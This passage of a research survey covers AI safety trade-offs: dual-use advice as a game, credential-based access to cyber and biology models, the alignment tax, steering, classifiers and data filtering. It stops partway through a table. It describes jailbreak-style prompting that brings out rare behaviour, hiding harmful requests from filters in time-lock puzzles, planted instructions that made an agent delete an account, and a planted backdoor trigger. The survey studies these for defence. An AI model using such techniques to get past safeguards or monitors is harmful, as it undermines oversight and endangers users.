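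*Towards Poisoning Robustness Certification for Natural Language Generation* (2026) does consider an attacker, one who tampers with the training data. It presents the first certified guarantees for models that write text, including agents that call tools. The outsider who plants an instruction in a contract instead attacks the finished assistant through what it reads, and needs no access to its training.

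## When the same answer helps both a defender and an attacker

An assistant can meet its specification on every input and still help the wrong person. Suppose the company's security officer asks the office assistant how an employee might smuggle contracts out. A good answer lists the gaps that the company should close, but a dishonest employee who asks the same question gets the same list and can use it to smuggle contracts out.

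Mattsson, Berker and colleagues (2026), in *Fundamental Impossibility Results in AI Safety*, begin with a milder case. They told Claude Opus 5.5, a language model made by Anthropic, that they wanted to make a coworker unhappy, and asked for strategies. The model declined. When they wrote instead that they suspected a coworker of planning this against them, it listed patterns to watch for, with examples. Anyone who wants the strategies can therefore get them by claiming to be the target. They also asked for an answer that would help only someone who was sincere. The model replied that no answer could do that completely, and suggested steps such as keeping notes and talking to a manager. These steps are hard to misuse but may be less useful than the list. Mattsson and colleagues use game theory to find out whether a cleverer adviser could avoid this trade-off.

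### An adviser that everyone can hear

In the first model, a defender and an attacker play a zero-sum game, in which one side gains exactly what the other loses. Both know the payoffs but have limited computing power. An AI adviser without that limit publishes advice that both can read.

For example, a company can watch either email or file uploads each day, and a thief chooses one of these routes. The company loses nothing if it watches the right one. Otherwise it loses 1 if the thief uses email and 3 if the thief uses uploads. Its best plan is to choose at random, watching email a quarter of the time and uploads the rest. It then loses an average of 3/4 a day, whichever route the thief takes. Game theorists call this the maximin strategy because it has the best guaranteed average result. The thief's best plan, the minimax strategy, is to choose at random too, using email three quarters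 of the time. The company then loses an average of 3/4 a day, whichever route it watches.

When each side has hundreds of options, the hard part is finding which ones are worth using. The attacker can work this out from the defender's best strategy, by noting which options it uses and keeping only the replies that do best against that mixture. The attacker then solves a system of linear equations to find probabilities for those replies that make all the options the defender uses equally good. In the example, if *q* is the share of days on which the thief uses email, the equation is 3(1 − *q*) = *q*, so *q* is 3/4. The method works for "generic" games, which have no coincidental ties between options and include almost all games.

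Such equations belong to DET, a class of problems that many processors working in parallel can solve very quickly. Finding the attacker's best strategy without advice is P-hard, which means that it is at least as hard as every problem that a computer can solve in polynomial time. Computer scientists conjecture that no amount of parallel hardware makes all of those problems fast. Mattsson and colleagues assume that the attacker can solve problems in DET and any problem that the defender can solve, but nothing harder. They prove that three conditions can't all hold:

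- Maximal helpfulness: in every game, the advice enables the defender to compute her best strategy.
- Non-maximal harmfulness: in at least one game, the attacker has too little information to compute his.
- No situational awareness: both sides receive the same advice and everything they need to interpret it, because the adviser does not know who is asking.

If everyone gets the same advice and it lets the defender compute her strategy, the attacker can compute her strategy too, and then his own. An adviser therefore can't give everyone the same advice, help the defender, and keep the attacker from computing his strategy all at once. It can meet any two of these conditions by telling only the defender, telling everyone, or saying nothing, provided that the attacker can't already solve every game unaided.

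The first condition is so strict that an adviser violates it by staying silent about one hard game in a million, and that adviser may then satisfy the second. The step from one strategy to the other is therefore more informative than the theorem, because it shows, for each game separately, that public advice giving the defender her best strategy also gives the attacker his.

The gap between DET and P is also small in practice, since an ordinary computer can solve games with thousands of options without advice. Mattsson and colleagues therefore add an example with a wider gap. A defender divides guards of different strengths between two sites, and an attacker sends a force with half the guards' total strength to one of them. The stronger side wins, and a tie is decided by a coin toss at the left site but goes to the defender at the right site. The attacker should choose the left site two thirds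 of the time if the guards can be split into two equally strong groups, and half the time if they can't. Deciding whether such a split exists is NP-complete, but the defender's best plan reveals the answer because it uses an equal split whenever there is one.

The theorem measures harm by what the attacker can compute, not by what the defender loses. In the first example, a company that follows the published plan loses 3/4 a day even if the thief has also read the plan. A company that never saw the advice is worse off. It might have lost less to a thief who chose badly, but a thief who has read the advice can ensure that it loses 3/4.

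### Facts that help only one side

In a second model, the players lack information instead of computing power. A treasure is equally likely to be in either of two places, and each player searches one. If only one player picks the right place, that player gets 1 and the other gets 0. If both or neither pick it, each gets 1/2.

Without advice, each player gets 1/2 on average. If the adviser tells only the defender where the treasure is, she always goes there. The attacker guesses correctly half the time, so the defender gets 1/2 in those cases and 1 in the others, or 3/4 on average. If the adviser tells both, they both go there and get 1/2 each. Public hints don't help the defender either, because the game is still the same for both players after any such hint.

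Other games have facts that only one side can use. In one such game, the world is in one of four equally likely states, and each player chooses between two options. In states A and B, only the defender's choice matters. She wins 1 if she chooses bottom in A or top in B, and otherwise gets 0. In states C and D, only the attacker's choice matters, and she gets 0 if he chooses left in C or right in D. The table gives the defender's average payoff if both players choose as well as they can.

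| Public advice | A | B | C | D | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1/2 | 1/2 | 1/2 | 1/2 | 1/2 |
| The exact state | 1 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 1/2 |
| The state only if it is A or B | 1 | 1 | 1/2 | 1/2 | 3/4 |

With the third policy, the attacker can infer from silence that the state is C or D, but not which, so he still has to guess. The defender gets 3/4, as much as she would get from complete private advice. A cautious assistant does something similar when it explains how to recognise and report a trick without explaining how to perform it. But separating the two kinds of fact can be difficult. Mattsson and colleagues cite a proof that finding the best public disclosure is NP-hard even for a restricted class of security games.

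### Where the model stops applying

Mattsson and colleagues chose zero-sum games because helping and harming have exact definitions there, but they do not think most real interactions are zero-sum. For example, someone who asks how to treat a burn usually has no opponent whom a good answer would harm, so the theorem gives no reason to withhold the answer.

Outside zero-sum games, an adviser can hurt the person it is trying to help. In one example, a defender is equally likely to be strong or weak, and an attacker who can't tell which makes a minor attack, leaving her with a payoff of 2. The outcome changes if an adviser can publish proof of the defender's strength. When she is strong, the adviser publishes it, the attacker stays away and she gets 3. But the attacker then takes silence as a sign of weakness and launches a major attack, which leaves a weak defender with −10. Her average payoff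 falls from 2 to −3.5. The adviser could prevent this by committing in advance to stay silent, if the attacker believed the commitment.

The model also assumes a single round of play, an adviser without limits and players who trust it. Over several rounds, an adviser might learn who is asking. Mattsson and colleagues suggest relaxing the first two conditions by having the adviser give approximate advice, although they expect competition between developers to discourage this. They do not calculate how much a given loss of accuracy would improve safety.

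### Behaviour that training makes rare

An adviser that withholds some answers must withhold them reliably. Developers train language models to refuse harmful requests, but *Fundamental Limitations of Alignment in Large Language Models* (Wolf, Avnery and colleagues, 2023) proves that, under certain assumptions, if training makes a behaviour rare without removing it, some prompt can still produce it.

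They describe a language model as a mixture of two components, one well behaved and one ill behaved. The probability of any text is

*P*(text) = *α* *P*₋(text) + (1 − *α*) *P*₊(text)

where *P*₋ is the ill-behaved component and *α* is its weight before the model receives a prompt. Training can make *α* tiny. But a prompt changes the weights by Bayes' rule, which multiplies the odds of the ill-behaved component by *P*₋(prompt)/*P*₊(prompt). Suppose *α* is one in a million, and some prompt consists of sentences that are each 100 times as probable under *P*₋ as under *P*₊. After three sentences the odds are about even, and after five they are 10,000 to 1. If training made the behaviour another thousand times rarer, the prompt would need only one and a half more sentences.

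In the theorem, a score from −1 to 1 measures how good a sentence is, and *β* is a lower limit on how much an average further sentence can favour the ill-behaved component, on a logarithmic scale. Some prompt of at most

(log(1/*α*) + log(1/*ε*) + log 4)/*β*

sentences then brings the model's average score down to within *ε* of the worst level that the ill-behaved component guarantees. Generating *n* answers and choosing the best adds only (log *n*)/*β* to this length.

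Almost every language model has a small probability of bad output, but the theorem requires more than that. The ill-behaved component must stay bad after every possible prompt, and further sentences must keep separating the two components. A model that refuses more firmly as a prompt becomes more suspicious does not meet these conditions, so the theorem alone can't show that a particular model is vulnerable. The theorem also assumes that the model's parameters are fixed and that nothing outside the model checks the prompt or the answer. Wolf and colleagues point out that limiting prompt length could therefore protect a model whose *α* is small enough.

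In their experiments with Llama 2 13B chat, an openly available model from 2023, behaviour deteriorated within a few sentences, roughly as the theory predicted. They could not extract the two components from the model, so they used separately trained models as stand-ins. They estimated that *β* was about five times as high in the model trained on human feedback as in the version without that training. They conjecture that training may make a behaviour rarer but also easier to single out.

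### Filters outside the model

Many developers use a separate program to check prompts before they reach the model, or answers before they reach the user. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) proves that, for some models, no prompt filter that runs much faster than the model can reliably tell harmful prompts from innocent ones. The proof relies on time-lock puzzles, a cryptographic tool that hides a message until somebody has done a fixed amount of computation. An attacker can hide a harmful request in a puzzle that the model has time to solve but the filter doesn't, so the filter can't distinguish the prompt from an innocent one.

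This result depends on several assumptions. Time-lock puzzles must exist, which cryptographers believe but have not proved. Innocent prompts must be varied enough to conceal a harmful one. The filter must be much weaker than the model, have no access to its internal workings, and let innocent prompts through with high probability. Ball and colleagues defend the assumption about the filter's strength by noting that if the filter were as powerful as the model, developers could use it in the model's place, and would then have to make the filter safe.

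The proof also uses a model built to defeat filters. Ball and colleagues admit that this is contrived, but reply that contrived weaknesses in cryptography have later caused real damage. They cite a 2016 theft of more than $60 million through a flaw in programs on Ethereum, a blockchain. Their argument is a good reason for caution about a model from an untrusted supplier. It is a weaker reason for caution about a model that a company trains itself, because a good filter may still exist for that model.

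Filters that check answers have an easier task, because the harm may be visible in the answer itself. Ball and colleagues grant that such a filter is trivial to build if harmful answers are easy to recognise. But they prove that for some models and some definitions of harm, no efficient filter can separate harmful answers from safe ones, even if it runs for longer than the model. This covers cases in which harm is hard to recognise, such as their example of a complex business plan that subtly recommends excluding clients with certain characteristics. Their theorem does not affect the procedure that looks for copied sentences in the office assistant's emails, because copied sentences are easy to recognise.

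They conclude that no filter outside a model can make it safe, and they make the same objection to proposals to use goalless question-answering systems as guards.

A security officer and a thief may send identical prompts, and the best answer may be the same for both. In that case, even a perfect filter could not block the thief without also blocking the officer.

### Learning who is asking

An adviser that can tell defenders from attackers no longer has to satisfy the third condition. Mattsson and colleagues discuss several ways to tell them apart. A developer could vet users in advance or encrypt advice so that only a known defender can read it. The AI system could also ask follow-up questions that a real target of harassment could answer more easily than a harasser. But an attacker can invent answers or behave well for several rounds, and has a reason to do so if the advice is worth more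 than the effort.

Vetting admits some attackers and excludes some defenders. The treasure game makes it possible to see how these errors add up. A defender without access who faces an attacker with access gets only 1/4 on average. If neither or both have access, she gets 1/2. If *d* is the probability that the defender has access and *a* the probability that the attacker does, her average payoff is therefore

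1/2 + (*d* − *a*)/4

A system that admits 90 per cent of defenders and 10 per cent of attackers raises her payoff to 0.7. One that admits 10 per cent of defenders and 1 per cent of attackers raises it only to about 0.52, even though it admits fewer attackers. If attackers get in more often than defenders, for example by using stolen accounts, everyone except the attackers would be better off without the adviser.

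*Access Controls Will Solve the Dual-Use Dilemma* (Wybitul, 2025) proposes basing access on credentials verified by a third party. The system sorts each answer into a risk category and checks whether the user has the credentials for it. It requires none for everyday questions, and it still refuses clearly harmful requests. Other questions fall in between. For example, a student, a vaccine researcher and someone planning an attack might all ask which features of viral surface proteins human antibodies recognise, and the wording doesn't reliably show which of them is asking. Wybitul suggests requiring an institutional email address and confirmation from the institution for advanced bioengineering, chemical synthesis and advanced cybersecurity.

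A separate program could do the sorting, but it might be too weak to interpret what the model writes. Wybitul therefore proposes putting the detector inside the model. During training, only examples from a risky field, such as advanced virology, would change a small "expert module", and a gate would learn to switch the module on whenever the model needs that knowledge. When the gate did so, a mechanism outside the model would block the answer unless the user was authorised. Since the gate is part of the model, the theorem about outside filters does not cover it.

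The guarantee would depend on the knowledge staying in the module. If the rest of the network also learned some virology, the model could answer without opening the gate or triggering a check. Researchers have trained such modules in smaller models, but nobody had tested the gated design in a large language model when Wybitul proposed it. Wybitul also acknowledges problems with privacy, unequal access and friction for users whom the system stops by mistake. The paper's title claims too much, because a credential that shows where somebody works doesn't show what they intend to do.

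### Fable and Mythos

According to Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026), the company already sells the same underlying model under two names. Fable is available to the public with strong safeguards in cybersecurity and biology, while organisations that work in cybersecurity or biomedical research can apply for Mythos. In Mattsson and colleagues' terms, Anthropic gives up maximal helpfulness for the public and learns who is asking before it offers more.

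Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2* explains that many questions flagged by Fable's safeguards go to a less capable model instead of being refused. In most of Anthropic's own applications, flagged cybersecurity questions go to Opus 4.8 and flagged biology questions go to Opus 5. A defender whose question is flagged may therefore still get an answer, but not the best one available.

Anthropic's *Cyber Verification Program* describes a three-level scheme through which security professionals can apply for fewer restrictions. The penetration tests mentioned in the table are authorised attacks meant to find weaknesses in a system.

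| Level | Examples of permitted work | Who may apply | Approved users | Target for a decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Defense Access | Responding to incidents, analysing malicious software | Organisations and individuals | No default limit | Two days |
| Red Team Access | Penetration tests, developing exploits | Organisations | Up to 75 | Two weeks |
| Specialized Access | Testing critical systems such as power grids | Organisations | Up to 25 | None |

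At every access level, Anthropic forbids extortion, mass destruction of data and any request with a stated malicious intent. The higher levels also require background checks and devices that the organisation controls. These measures make it harder to misuse an account, but an approved tester could still turn dishonest. Anthropic reserves the right to withdraw access if it sees violations, and detecting them requires keeping records of what people ask.

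Applicants give up some privacy. Individuals need a government photo ID and may have to take a live selfie. Organisations provide their legal name, address and registration number. Helton's *I'm Sorry Dave, This Request Triggered Restrictions On Violative Cyber Content* compares this to the identity checks banks must run on customers, and notes that offensive security research can no longer come from an anonymous account.

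The public version also reduces customers' privacy. Anthropic's *Covered Models* says that, by default, the company keeps prompts and answers from all Fable and Mythos models for at least 30 days, and automated systems review them. Anthropic's stated reason is that some misuse can be detected only across many requests. But the rule also covers the great majority of customers, who have nothing to do with cyberattacks or pathogens. Constellation Research's *Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.1, Mythos 5.1 launch addresses price and data retention* reports that customers objected. In response, Anthropic plans to let organisations store the records in cloud systems they control, and in the meantime it lets some eligible customers use Fable without retention.

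The restrictions on access mainly affect people without an institution behind them. The scheme is closed to users of Anthropic's free plan, and an independent researcher can apply only for Defense Access. A small testing firm without a recognised accreditation or similar proof can qualify for Red Team Access only if it has been registered for at least a year and employs at least two certified testers. In December 2026, decisions at that level were taking longer than the two-week target because of high demand. OpenAI, which makes ChatGPT, has a comparable scheme for biology. OpenAI's *Life Science Research Special Access Program* says the scheme is open only to select institutions that have service agreements with the company, and concedes that the standard safeguards "can create high friction for some researchers".

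Early access to Mythos was narrower still. On 2 June 2026, Bloomberg's *Anthropic Offers Mythos Model Access to 150 Additional Groups* reported that about 200 organisations had access. A week later, Anthropic released the first version of Fable to the public. Anthropic's *Bringing the cybersecurity capabilities of Claude Mythos 5 to more defenders* later announced 35 million dollars in credits for organisations that help open-source maintainers, many of whom are volunteers whose code large companies depend on.

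Governments can also decide who counts as a defender. In June, *Cyber Experts Urge US to Lift Ban on Anthropic’s Frontier AI Models* (Poireault, 2026) reported that the Trump administration had effectively barred everyone who was not a US national from Fable 5 and Mythos 5. According to DIGIT, Anthropic said the restrictions came after Amazon researchers found a way around Fable's safeguards. *White House Clears Claude Fable 5 and Mythos 5 After Cyber Review* (Ticong, 2026) reported that the White House had cleared both models by 1 July. Mythos at first returned only to a group of US organisations, so defenders abroad had to wait longer for the version without Fable's safeguards. Anthropic still reviews every application for Specialized Access with the US government.

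## What safety training and filtering cost in measured ability

Vetting users mainly affects people who ask about sensitive subjects, but safety training changes a model for everyone, so developers also measure its effect on ordinary work. *Safety Alignment as Continual Learning* (Sun, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) measures the alignment tax as a model's score on a set of general tests before safety training minus its score afterwards. For example, a model that scores 70 per cent before and 67 per cent after has an alignment tax of 3 percentage points.

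The measured loss of ability depends on which tests are used. Suppose a model refuses one in five harmless questions about poisons after safety training. A mathematics test contains no such questions, so the measured loss may be zero, although a toxicologist would notice the refusals. The measurement also omits the computation used for extra training and for programs that check each answer.

Comparisons of test scores also leave out the effect of delay. If a developer holds back a model because it fails a safety test, customers have to keep using older models in the meantime.

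Small losses in ability are hard to measure. *EvalSafetyGap* (Ulurmak and Kurban, 2026) cites an analysis of 60 widely used benchmarks, 29 of which were highly saturated, meaning that the best models' scores were too close together to tell the models apart. It also cites a review of 445 articles about benchmarks, only 16 per cent of which used error estimates or statistical tests to compare results. Chance affects scores most on short tests. AIME 2024, a mathematics competition used in several of the studies below, has 30 problems, so one more mistake lowers the score by 3.3 percentage points.

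### From early assistants to reasoning models

*Toward Alignment Scaling Laws* (Canale, 2026) recounts two early findings. OpenAI's InstructGPT, a language model trained on human ratings of its answers, scored lower on some public language tests after that training. Its developers greatly reduced the loss by mixing ordinary training text into the later training. In another early study, training on human feedback lowered the scores of models with fewer than about 10 billion parameters but raised those of models with 13 and 52 billion. *A Comprehensive Survey on Trustworthiness in Reasoning with Large Language Models* (2025) describes a later study that found losses in translation, reading comprehension and question answering. Merging the parameters of different versions of the model worked best against these losses, though a slight loss remained.

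Those models answered immediately, but by 2025 the leading models reasoned at length first. In *Safety Tax*, Huang, Hu and colleagues (2025) found much larger losses in such reasoning models. They started with s1.1-32B, which other researchers had made by training an ordinary model, Qwen-32B-instruct, on worked solutions. They then trained it for five passes over 1,000 harmful questions with refusals as answers. They tried both DirectRefusal, a data set in which the same short thought precedes every refusal, and SafeChain, whose examples contain long reasoning.

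The table gives the results in per cent. GPQA contains graduate-level science questions, and MATH-500 contains mathematics problems. The last column is the share of 1,000 harmful test questions that a separate classifier judged the model to have answered harmfully.

| Stage | AIME 2024 | GPQA | MATH-500 | Average | Harmful answers |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before reasoning training | 16.7 | 40.4 | 65.2 | 40.8 | 16.7 |
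| After reasoning training | 40.0 | 58.6 | 91.6 | 63.4 | 60.4 |
| Then DirectRefusal | 13.3 | 35.4 | 48.8 | 32.5 | 0.8 |
| Then SafeChain | 30.0 | 51.5 | 87.4 | 56.3 | 30.8 |

DirectRefusal almost eliminated harmful answers, but it lowered the model's reasoning score by 31 points, leaving it weaker than before its reasoning training. DirectRefusal training took only ten minutes on eight processors, so the main loss was in ability. SafeChain lowered the score by only 7 points, but the model still answered almost a third of the harmful questions. Losing ability doesn't always make a model safer. With another model, LIMO-32B, SafeChain lowered the GPQA score by 8 points while harmful answers rose slightly, from 29.5 to 30.5 per cent.

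Huang and colleagues concluded that the trade-off seems unavoidable when safety training follows reasoning training in this way, but their experiment can't establish that. The safety stage contained only refusals, with no mathematics to maintain the model's skill, and they did not test an equal amount of training on short answers to harmless questions. DirectRefusal may have done so much damage because every example taught the model to stop reasoning early.

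### Training methods that reduce the loss

Xie, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Mitigating Safety Tax via Distribution-Grounded Refinement in Large Reasoning Models*, suspected that the loss of ability came from who had written the training examples. Safety data usually comes from another model or from people, so training on it also pulls the model towards a way of reasoning that isn't its own. The researchers therefore asked the model to rewrite each example's reasoning and answer in its own words before training on them. They kept the original if the rewrite ran past 5,000 tokens or commented on the task instead of doing it.

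They tested this on s1.1-7B, a smaller relative of Huang's model, which averaged 57.8 per cent on four reasoning tests. Training on the original DirectRefusal lowered the average to 18.5 per cent, while training on the rewritten version lowered it only to 48.7, which is still a large loss of 9 points. The rewriting also reduced safety somewhat, raising the share of unsafe answers on WildJailbreak, a set of disguised harmful requests, from 1.2 to 8.8 per cent.

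Their results also show how much a safety score depends on the test. After training on R1-ACT, another data set, the model gave safe answers to an average of 98 per cent of questions across three tests, but harmful answers to 40 per cent of questions in a fourth, which also used a different classifier as the judge.

Sun, Zhang and colleagues changed the training steps instead of the data. A model learns by making small changes to its parameters that reduce a "loss", a number that measures how badly it does on some examples. The gradient is the direction in which the loss rises fastest, so each step goes the opposite way. A step that improves safety can make the model worse at something else. Their method, orthogonal gradient projection, removes the part of each safety step that would affect chosen abilities. With only two parameters it works like this:

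1. Compute the gradient of the loss on a few examples of general ability. Suppose it is (3, 4).
2. Compute the gradient of the safety loss, say (5, −10). With a step size of 0.01, an ordinary step changes the parameters by (−0.05, 0.10). This lowers the safety loss by about 1.25 but raises the ability loss by 3 × (−0.05) + 4 × 0.10 = 0.25.
3. Subtract from the safety gradient its component along (3, 4). What remains is (8, −6), which is at right angles to (3, 4) because 3 × 8 − 4 × 6 = 0.
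4. Change the parameters by (−0.08, 0.06) instead. The safety loss falls by about 1.00, and the ability loss stays the same.

These figures assume both losses have constant slopes, which is accurate only for very small steps. In a real model the slopes change during training, so the ability gradients must be recomputed regularly. Sun and colleagues used two ability gradients, one for helpful answers and one for truthful ones, each computed from about 200 examples. When they never recomputed these gradients, the model did no better on factual questions than with ordinary training.

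They tested the method on Qwen2.5-7B and Llama 3.1-8B, with 10,000 safety examples. Two stages of ordinary safety training lowered the plain average of six general tests by 5.1 points for Qwen and 6.3 for Llama, while projection reduced these losses to 1.9 and 1.4 points. Projection also made Llama somewhat less safe, as its score on StrongREJECT, a test of harmful requests, fell from 99.9 to 94.5. Qwen's score rose slightly. Their headline result, a rise in Qwen's "average gain" from 34 to 43 per cent, is harder to interpret because it averages relative changes over ten tests, four of them about safety. Most of the rise comes from SimpleQA, a test of short factual questions on which the model got 3.0 per cent right instead of 0.5.

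Projection took 2 hours 56 minutes for a single training stage with Qwen, compared with 1 hour 49 minutes for ordinary training and just over four hours for training on a mixture with 10,000 general examples. After this stage, an automated attack still succeeded against the model 26 per cent of the time, down from 82 per cent before safety training. Sun and colleagues do not claim a global guarantee that either safety or ability will survive.

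### A small tax with many refusals

*SAVeR²* (Sun, Liu and colleagues, 2026) also reports that its method effectively eliminates the safety tax. The method rewards a reasoning model for recognising harmful intent, keeping both its reasoning and its answer harmless, making the two agree, and offering useful advice even when it refuses. It also projects gradients, but only when safety and reasoning conflict, so it doesn't alter safety updates that improve reasoning.

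They prove that the total loss of reasoning is at most

(*L*/2) × the sum over all steps of (step size)² × (length of the update)²

where *L* limits how fast the slope of the reasoning score can change. Small steps make this bound small, but it gives no figure in points unless somebody knows *L*. It also covers reasoning as the training rewards measure it, not every ability a user might care about.

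In tests on DeepSeek-R1-Distill-Qwen-7B, the average over five ability tests fell only from 65.5 to 64.8 per cent, but the score on LiveCodeBench, a programming test, fell from 39.8 to 33.7 per cent. Small gains on three of the other tests made up for less than half of that fall. The models were also asked harmless questions that resemble harmful ones, such as how to kill a frozen computer program. The original model refused 4.7 per cent of them, while a version trained by the new method without harmless examples refused 47.7 per cent. The 64.8 per cent ability average appears to come from this version, since the published safety scores are identical. Adding harmless examples to the training reduced refusals to 22.3 per cent, but the average on two safety tests fell from 99.0 to 96.1.

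These questions are deliberately tricky, so a model would refuse far fewer requests in everyday use. Still, refusals of these questions rose tenfold while measured ability fell by less than one point.

Refusals can do more damage when a model works as an agent. Li and Zhao (2026), in *Agent Safety Is Action Alignment*, cite experiments on models trained to reject planted instructions. These models failed at the first step of 47 to 77 per cent of harmless tasks, compared with 3 per cent for the model without this training. When an agent refused a harmless step, the software retried with the same wording and got the same refusal. The share of tasks that ran out of time rose from 13 per cent to as much as 99 per cent.

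The training didn't reliably stop attacks either. One planted request asked the agent to delete a user's account as part of a quality test. The untrained model refused, but a trained one deleted the account. Attacks of this kind succeeded 78 per cent of the time. Li and Zhao argue that no training on inputs and outputs can make actions safe, because the text doesn't reveal what the user has authorised. The experiments support the narrower conclusion that these defences had learned to recognise suspicious wording. A developer can also state some permissions in the prompt, though the model may ignore them.

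### Steering a finished model

Steering changes a model's internal states while it answers, without changing its parameters. Researchers run the model on pairs of good and bad examples, find the direction in which its internal states differ, and add a multiple of that direction to the states in its layers. The multiple, *r*, is the strength of the intervention.

Wolf, Wies and colleagues (2024), in *Tradeoffs Between Alignment and Helpfulness in Language Models with Steering Methods*, prove two bounds. The first says that steering multiplies the odds of a good answer by at least e^(2*cr*), where *c* depends on how cleanly the added direction separates good answers from bad ones. The second concerns unrelated questions, on which steering acts like random noise. If the model would answer such a question correctly with probability *P*, then in the tightest case the probability after steering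 is at most

*P* / (*P* + (1 − *P*)(1 + *k*²*r*²/2))

where *k* measures the noise. Their experiments gave values of 0.5 to 3 for *c* and 0.33 to 0.66 for *k*. The table uses *c* = 1 and *k* = 0.5, for a model that starts with 25 per cent good answers and 80 per cent correct ones.

| Strength *r* | Good answers, at least (%) | Correct answers, at most (%) |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 25 | 80 |
| 0.5 | 48 | 79.5 |
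| 1 | 71 | 78 |
| 2.5 | 98 | 69 |
| 5 | 99.99 | 49 |

When the steering strength *r* is small, the gain in good answers is roughly *ar* and the loss of correct ones is roughly *br*², for some constants *a* and *b*. Halving the strength halves the gain but cuts the loss to a quarter. The loss per unit of gain is (*b*/*a*)*r*, which approaches zero as *r* does. If a developer values a point of each equally, the best strength in this range is *a*/(2*b*), and some steering is always better than none. Replacing one strong steering step with ten weak ones in the same direction does not avoid the loss, because their strengths add up.

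This reasoning assumes that the loss follows the second formula, which is only an upper limit on correct answers. The true loss could be larger, so the case for weak steering depends on the experiments. With Llama 2 13B and its chat version, a steering strength of 2.5 was enough to turn each behaviour tested from mostly one way to mostly the other. Wolf and colleagues judged the loss on multiple-choice questions at that strength to be "not too great". Programming scores also peaked near zero strength and fell slowly at first.

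They also present steering, if strong enough, as a way to guarantee a good answer to any hostile prompt. The guarantee holds only if the added direction also separates good answers from bad ones on the attacker's prompt, and nobody can check this in advance for every prompt. Steering that strongly may also greatly reduce accuracy on ordinary questions. If a prompt makes a bad answer a million times as likely as a good one, the model in the table needs a strength of about 6.9 just to make the two equally likely. At that strength it would answer at most 36 per cent of ordinary questions correctly.

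Wolf and colleagues note that training has an advantage here because many small parameter changes don't necessarily disturb other abilities at random. Gradient projection deliberately uses this freedom.

### Classifiers that check prompts and answers

A developer can also leave the model unchanged and have a separate classifier check its inputs and outputs. The model's test scores then stay the same, except where the classifier blocks a harmless question, but running the classifier takes extra computation. *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025) describes such a system for Anthropic's Claude models. The researchers estimated the added computation by counting the tokens each classifier would read and write for 1,000 real Claude.ai exchanges, and found no significant increase. The classifier that checks answers produces only a score, which takes less computation than having a model write out its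 reasoning about every exchange.

The newest published version, *Constitutional Classifiers++* (2026), saves more compute by reusing values the protected model has already computed. A linear probe takes a weighted sum of these internal values and treats a high total as a warning. The probe alone was nearly as hard to defeat as the separate classifiers, and combining the two improved protection and reduced compute. Such a probe can also select which exchanges a more compute-intensive classifier checks. If it selected one exchange in twenty, that classifier would use about a twentieth as much compute.

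The researchers set every system in this comparison to refuse 0.1 per cent of the conversations in WildChat, a collection of real chats. Even this low rate affects a very large number of people. Suppose ten in a million conversations are dangerous. A classifier that catches all ten and wrongly blocks 0.1 per cent of the rest would block about 1,000 harmless conversations, or 100 for each dangerous one.

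Keeping wrongful refusals low also limits how many attacks a weaker detector can catch. *Conf-Guard* (2026) reports that Llama Guard 3, an openly available classifier, missed 84 per cent of one set of attacks spread over several messages when it could wrongly refuse 1 per cent of harmless conversations. It missed 63 per cent when it could wrongly refuse 5 per cent, and 57 per cent when it could wrongly refuse 15 per cent. Each figure for missed attacks is uncertain by 8 to 10 percentage points. Changing the refusal threshold also cannot separate a defender from an attacker who asks the same question.

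The refusal rate for everyday chats is a poor guide to how often models refuse specialists. *BioFirewall* (2026) tested three Claude models as screeners of biological sequences, a job meant to prevent harm. Claude Sonnet 5 refused to screen 83 per cent of the toxins and 38 per cent of the harmless sequences. Claude Opus 4.8 refused 76 and 7 per cent. Claude Haiku 4.5 refused none, but it let every toxin through. A laboratory could not rely on any of the three alone for automatic screening.

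### Changing what a model learns from

Other researchers remove dangerous material before training begins. *Deep Ignorance* (2025) describes a filter for text related to biological threats. Most biology is harmless, so the researchers trained a classifier on documents labelled by experts to separate dangerous text from the rest. Such filtering can leave a model without knowledge of a chosen technical subject, so the model does not have to refuse requests in order to protect that knowledge.

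Filtering hurts people who have a good use for the knowledge it removes. *The Effectiveness and Durability of Pretraining Data Filtering in Protein Language Models* (2026) gives the example of ESM3-open, a protein model that filtering made much worse at predicting how mutations affect viral proteins but hardly affected on other proteins. Averaged over all proteins, the loss would look small, but someone designing a vaccine would lose most of the model's benefit. Outsiders can also partly reverse filtering if they can train the model further. The developers of Evo 2, a genome model, excluded viral genomes from its training data, but additional training on those genomes improved some of its dangerous abilities.

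*Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering* (2026) suggests giving the public a filtered model and trusted users a complete one. The developer would not have to train both from scratch. Most of the effect of filtering appears early, so the developer could add the missing material later with reasonable resources, while an attacker would still need substantial resources to do the same. Trusted users would need some form of vetting, which brings errors and a loss of privacy.

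Training text about AI also affects a model's behaviour. In *Alignment Pretraining*, Tice, Radmard and colleagues (2026) trained models of 6.9 billion parameters from scratch on 500 billion tokens. They gave them short scenarios with two possible actions, one of them misaligned, such as avoiding a shutdown. The model trained on unfiltered data chose the misaligned action 45 per cent of the time. Filtering out most discussion of AI, about 9 per cent of the training data, reduced this to 31 per cent and lowered the average score on seven ability tests by about one point.

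Adding material worked better. When about 1 per cent of the training text described AI systems behaving well in difficult situations, the model chose the misaligned action only 9 per cent of the time. On questions for which Tice and colleagues had written no matching documents, the rate also fell, from 40 to 6 per cent. The average ability score after later training fell from 49 to 45 per cent, but scores on two reasoning tests fell by 11 points each. Adding the documents only near the end of training limited the average loss to about 2 points. Each version was trained only once, because a run took some 20,000 processor-hours, so part of these differences may be chance.

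### Larger models and hidden behaviour

The small losses of ability measured today would be a poor guide to larger models if safety training took more effort as models grew. In October 2026 Canale published a study with methods and decision rules registered in advance. Canale measures the effort needed to reduce a fault to a fixed rate, assuming that it grows as *aN*^*α*, where *N* is the number of parameters. If *α* is 0.5, a model 100 times as large needs ten times the effort, so a developer whose safety budget grows in proportion to model size would spend a shrinking share of it. The share would grow if *α* were above 1.

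Canale corrected faults in Qwen2.5 models with 0.5 to 72 billion parameters by training small add-on modules. A correction counted only if the model's score on MMLU, a test of general knowledge, stayed within 2 points of its starting value. For the last two rows of the table, Canale used models with up to 14 billion parameters and planted a backdoor that made them write "I HATE YOU" after a trigger phrase.

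| Fault | Highest rate allowed (%) | *α* for computing cost | Range |
|---|---|---|---|
| Choosing false answers | 10 | −0.05 | −0.58 to 0.33 |
| Stating risky preferences, such as seeking power | 5 | 0.48 | 0.30 to 0.65 |
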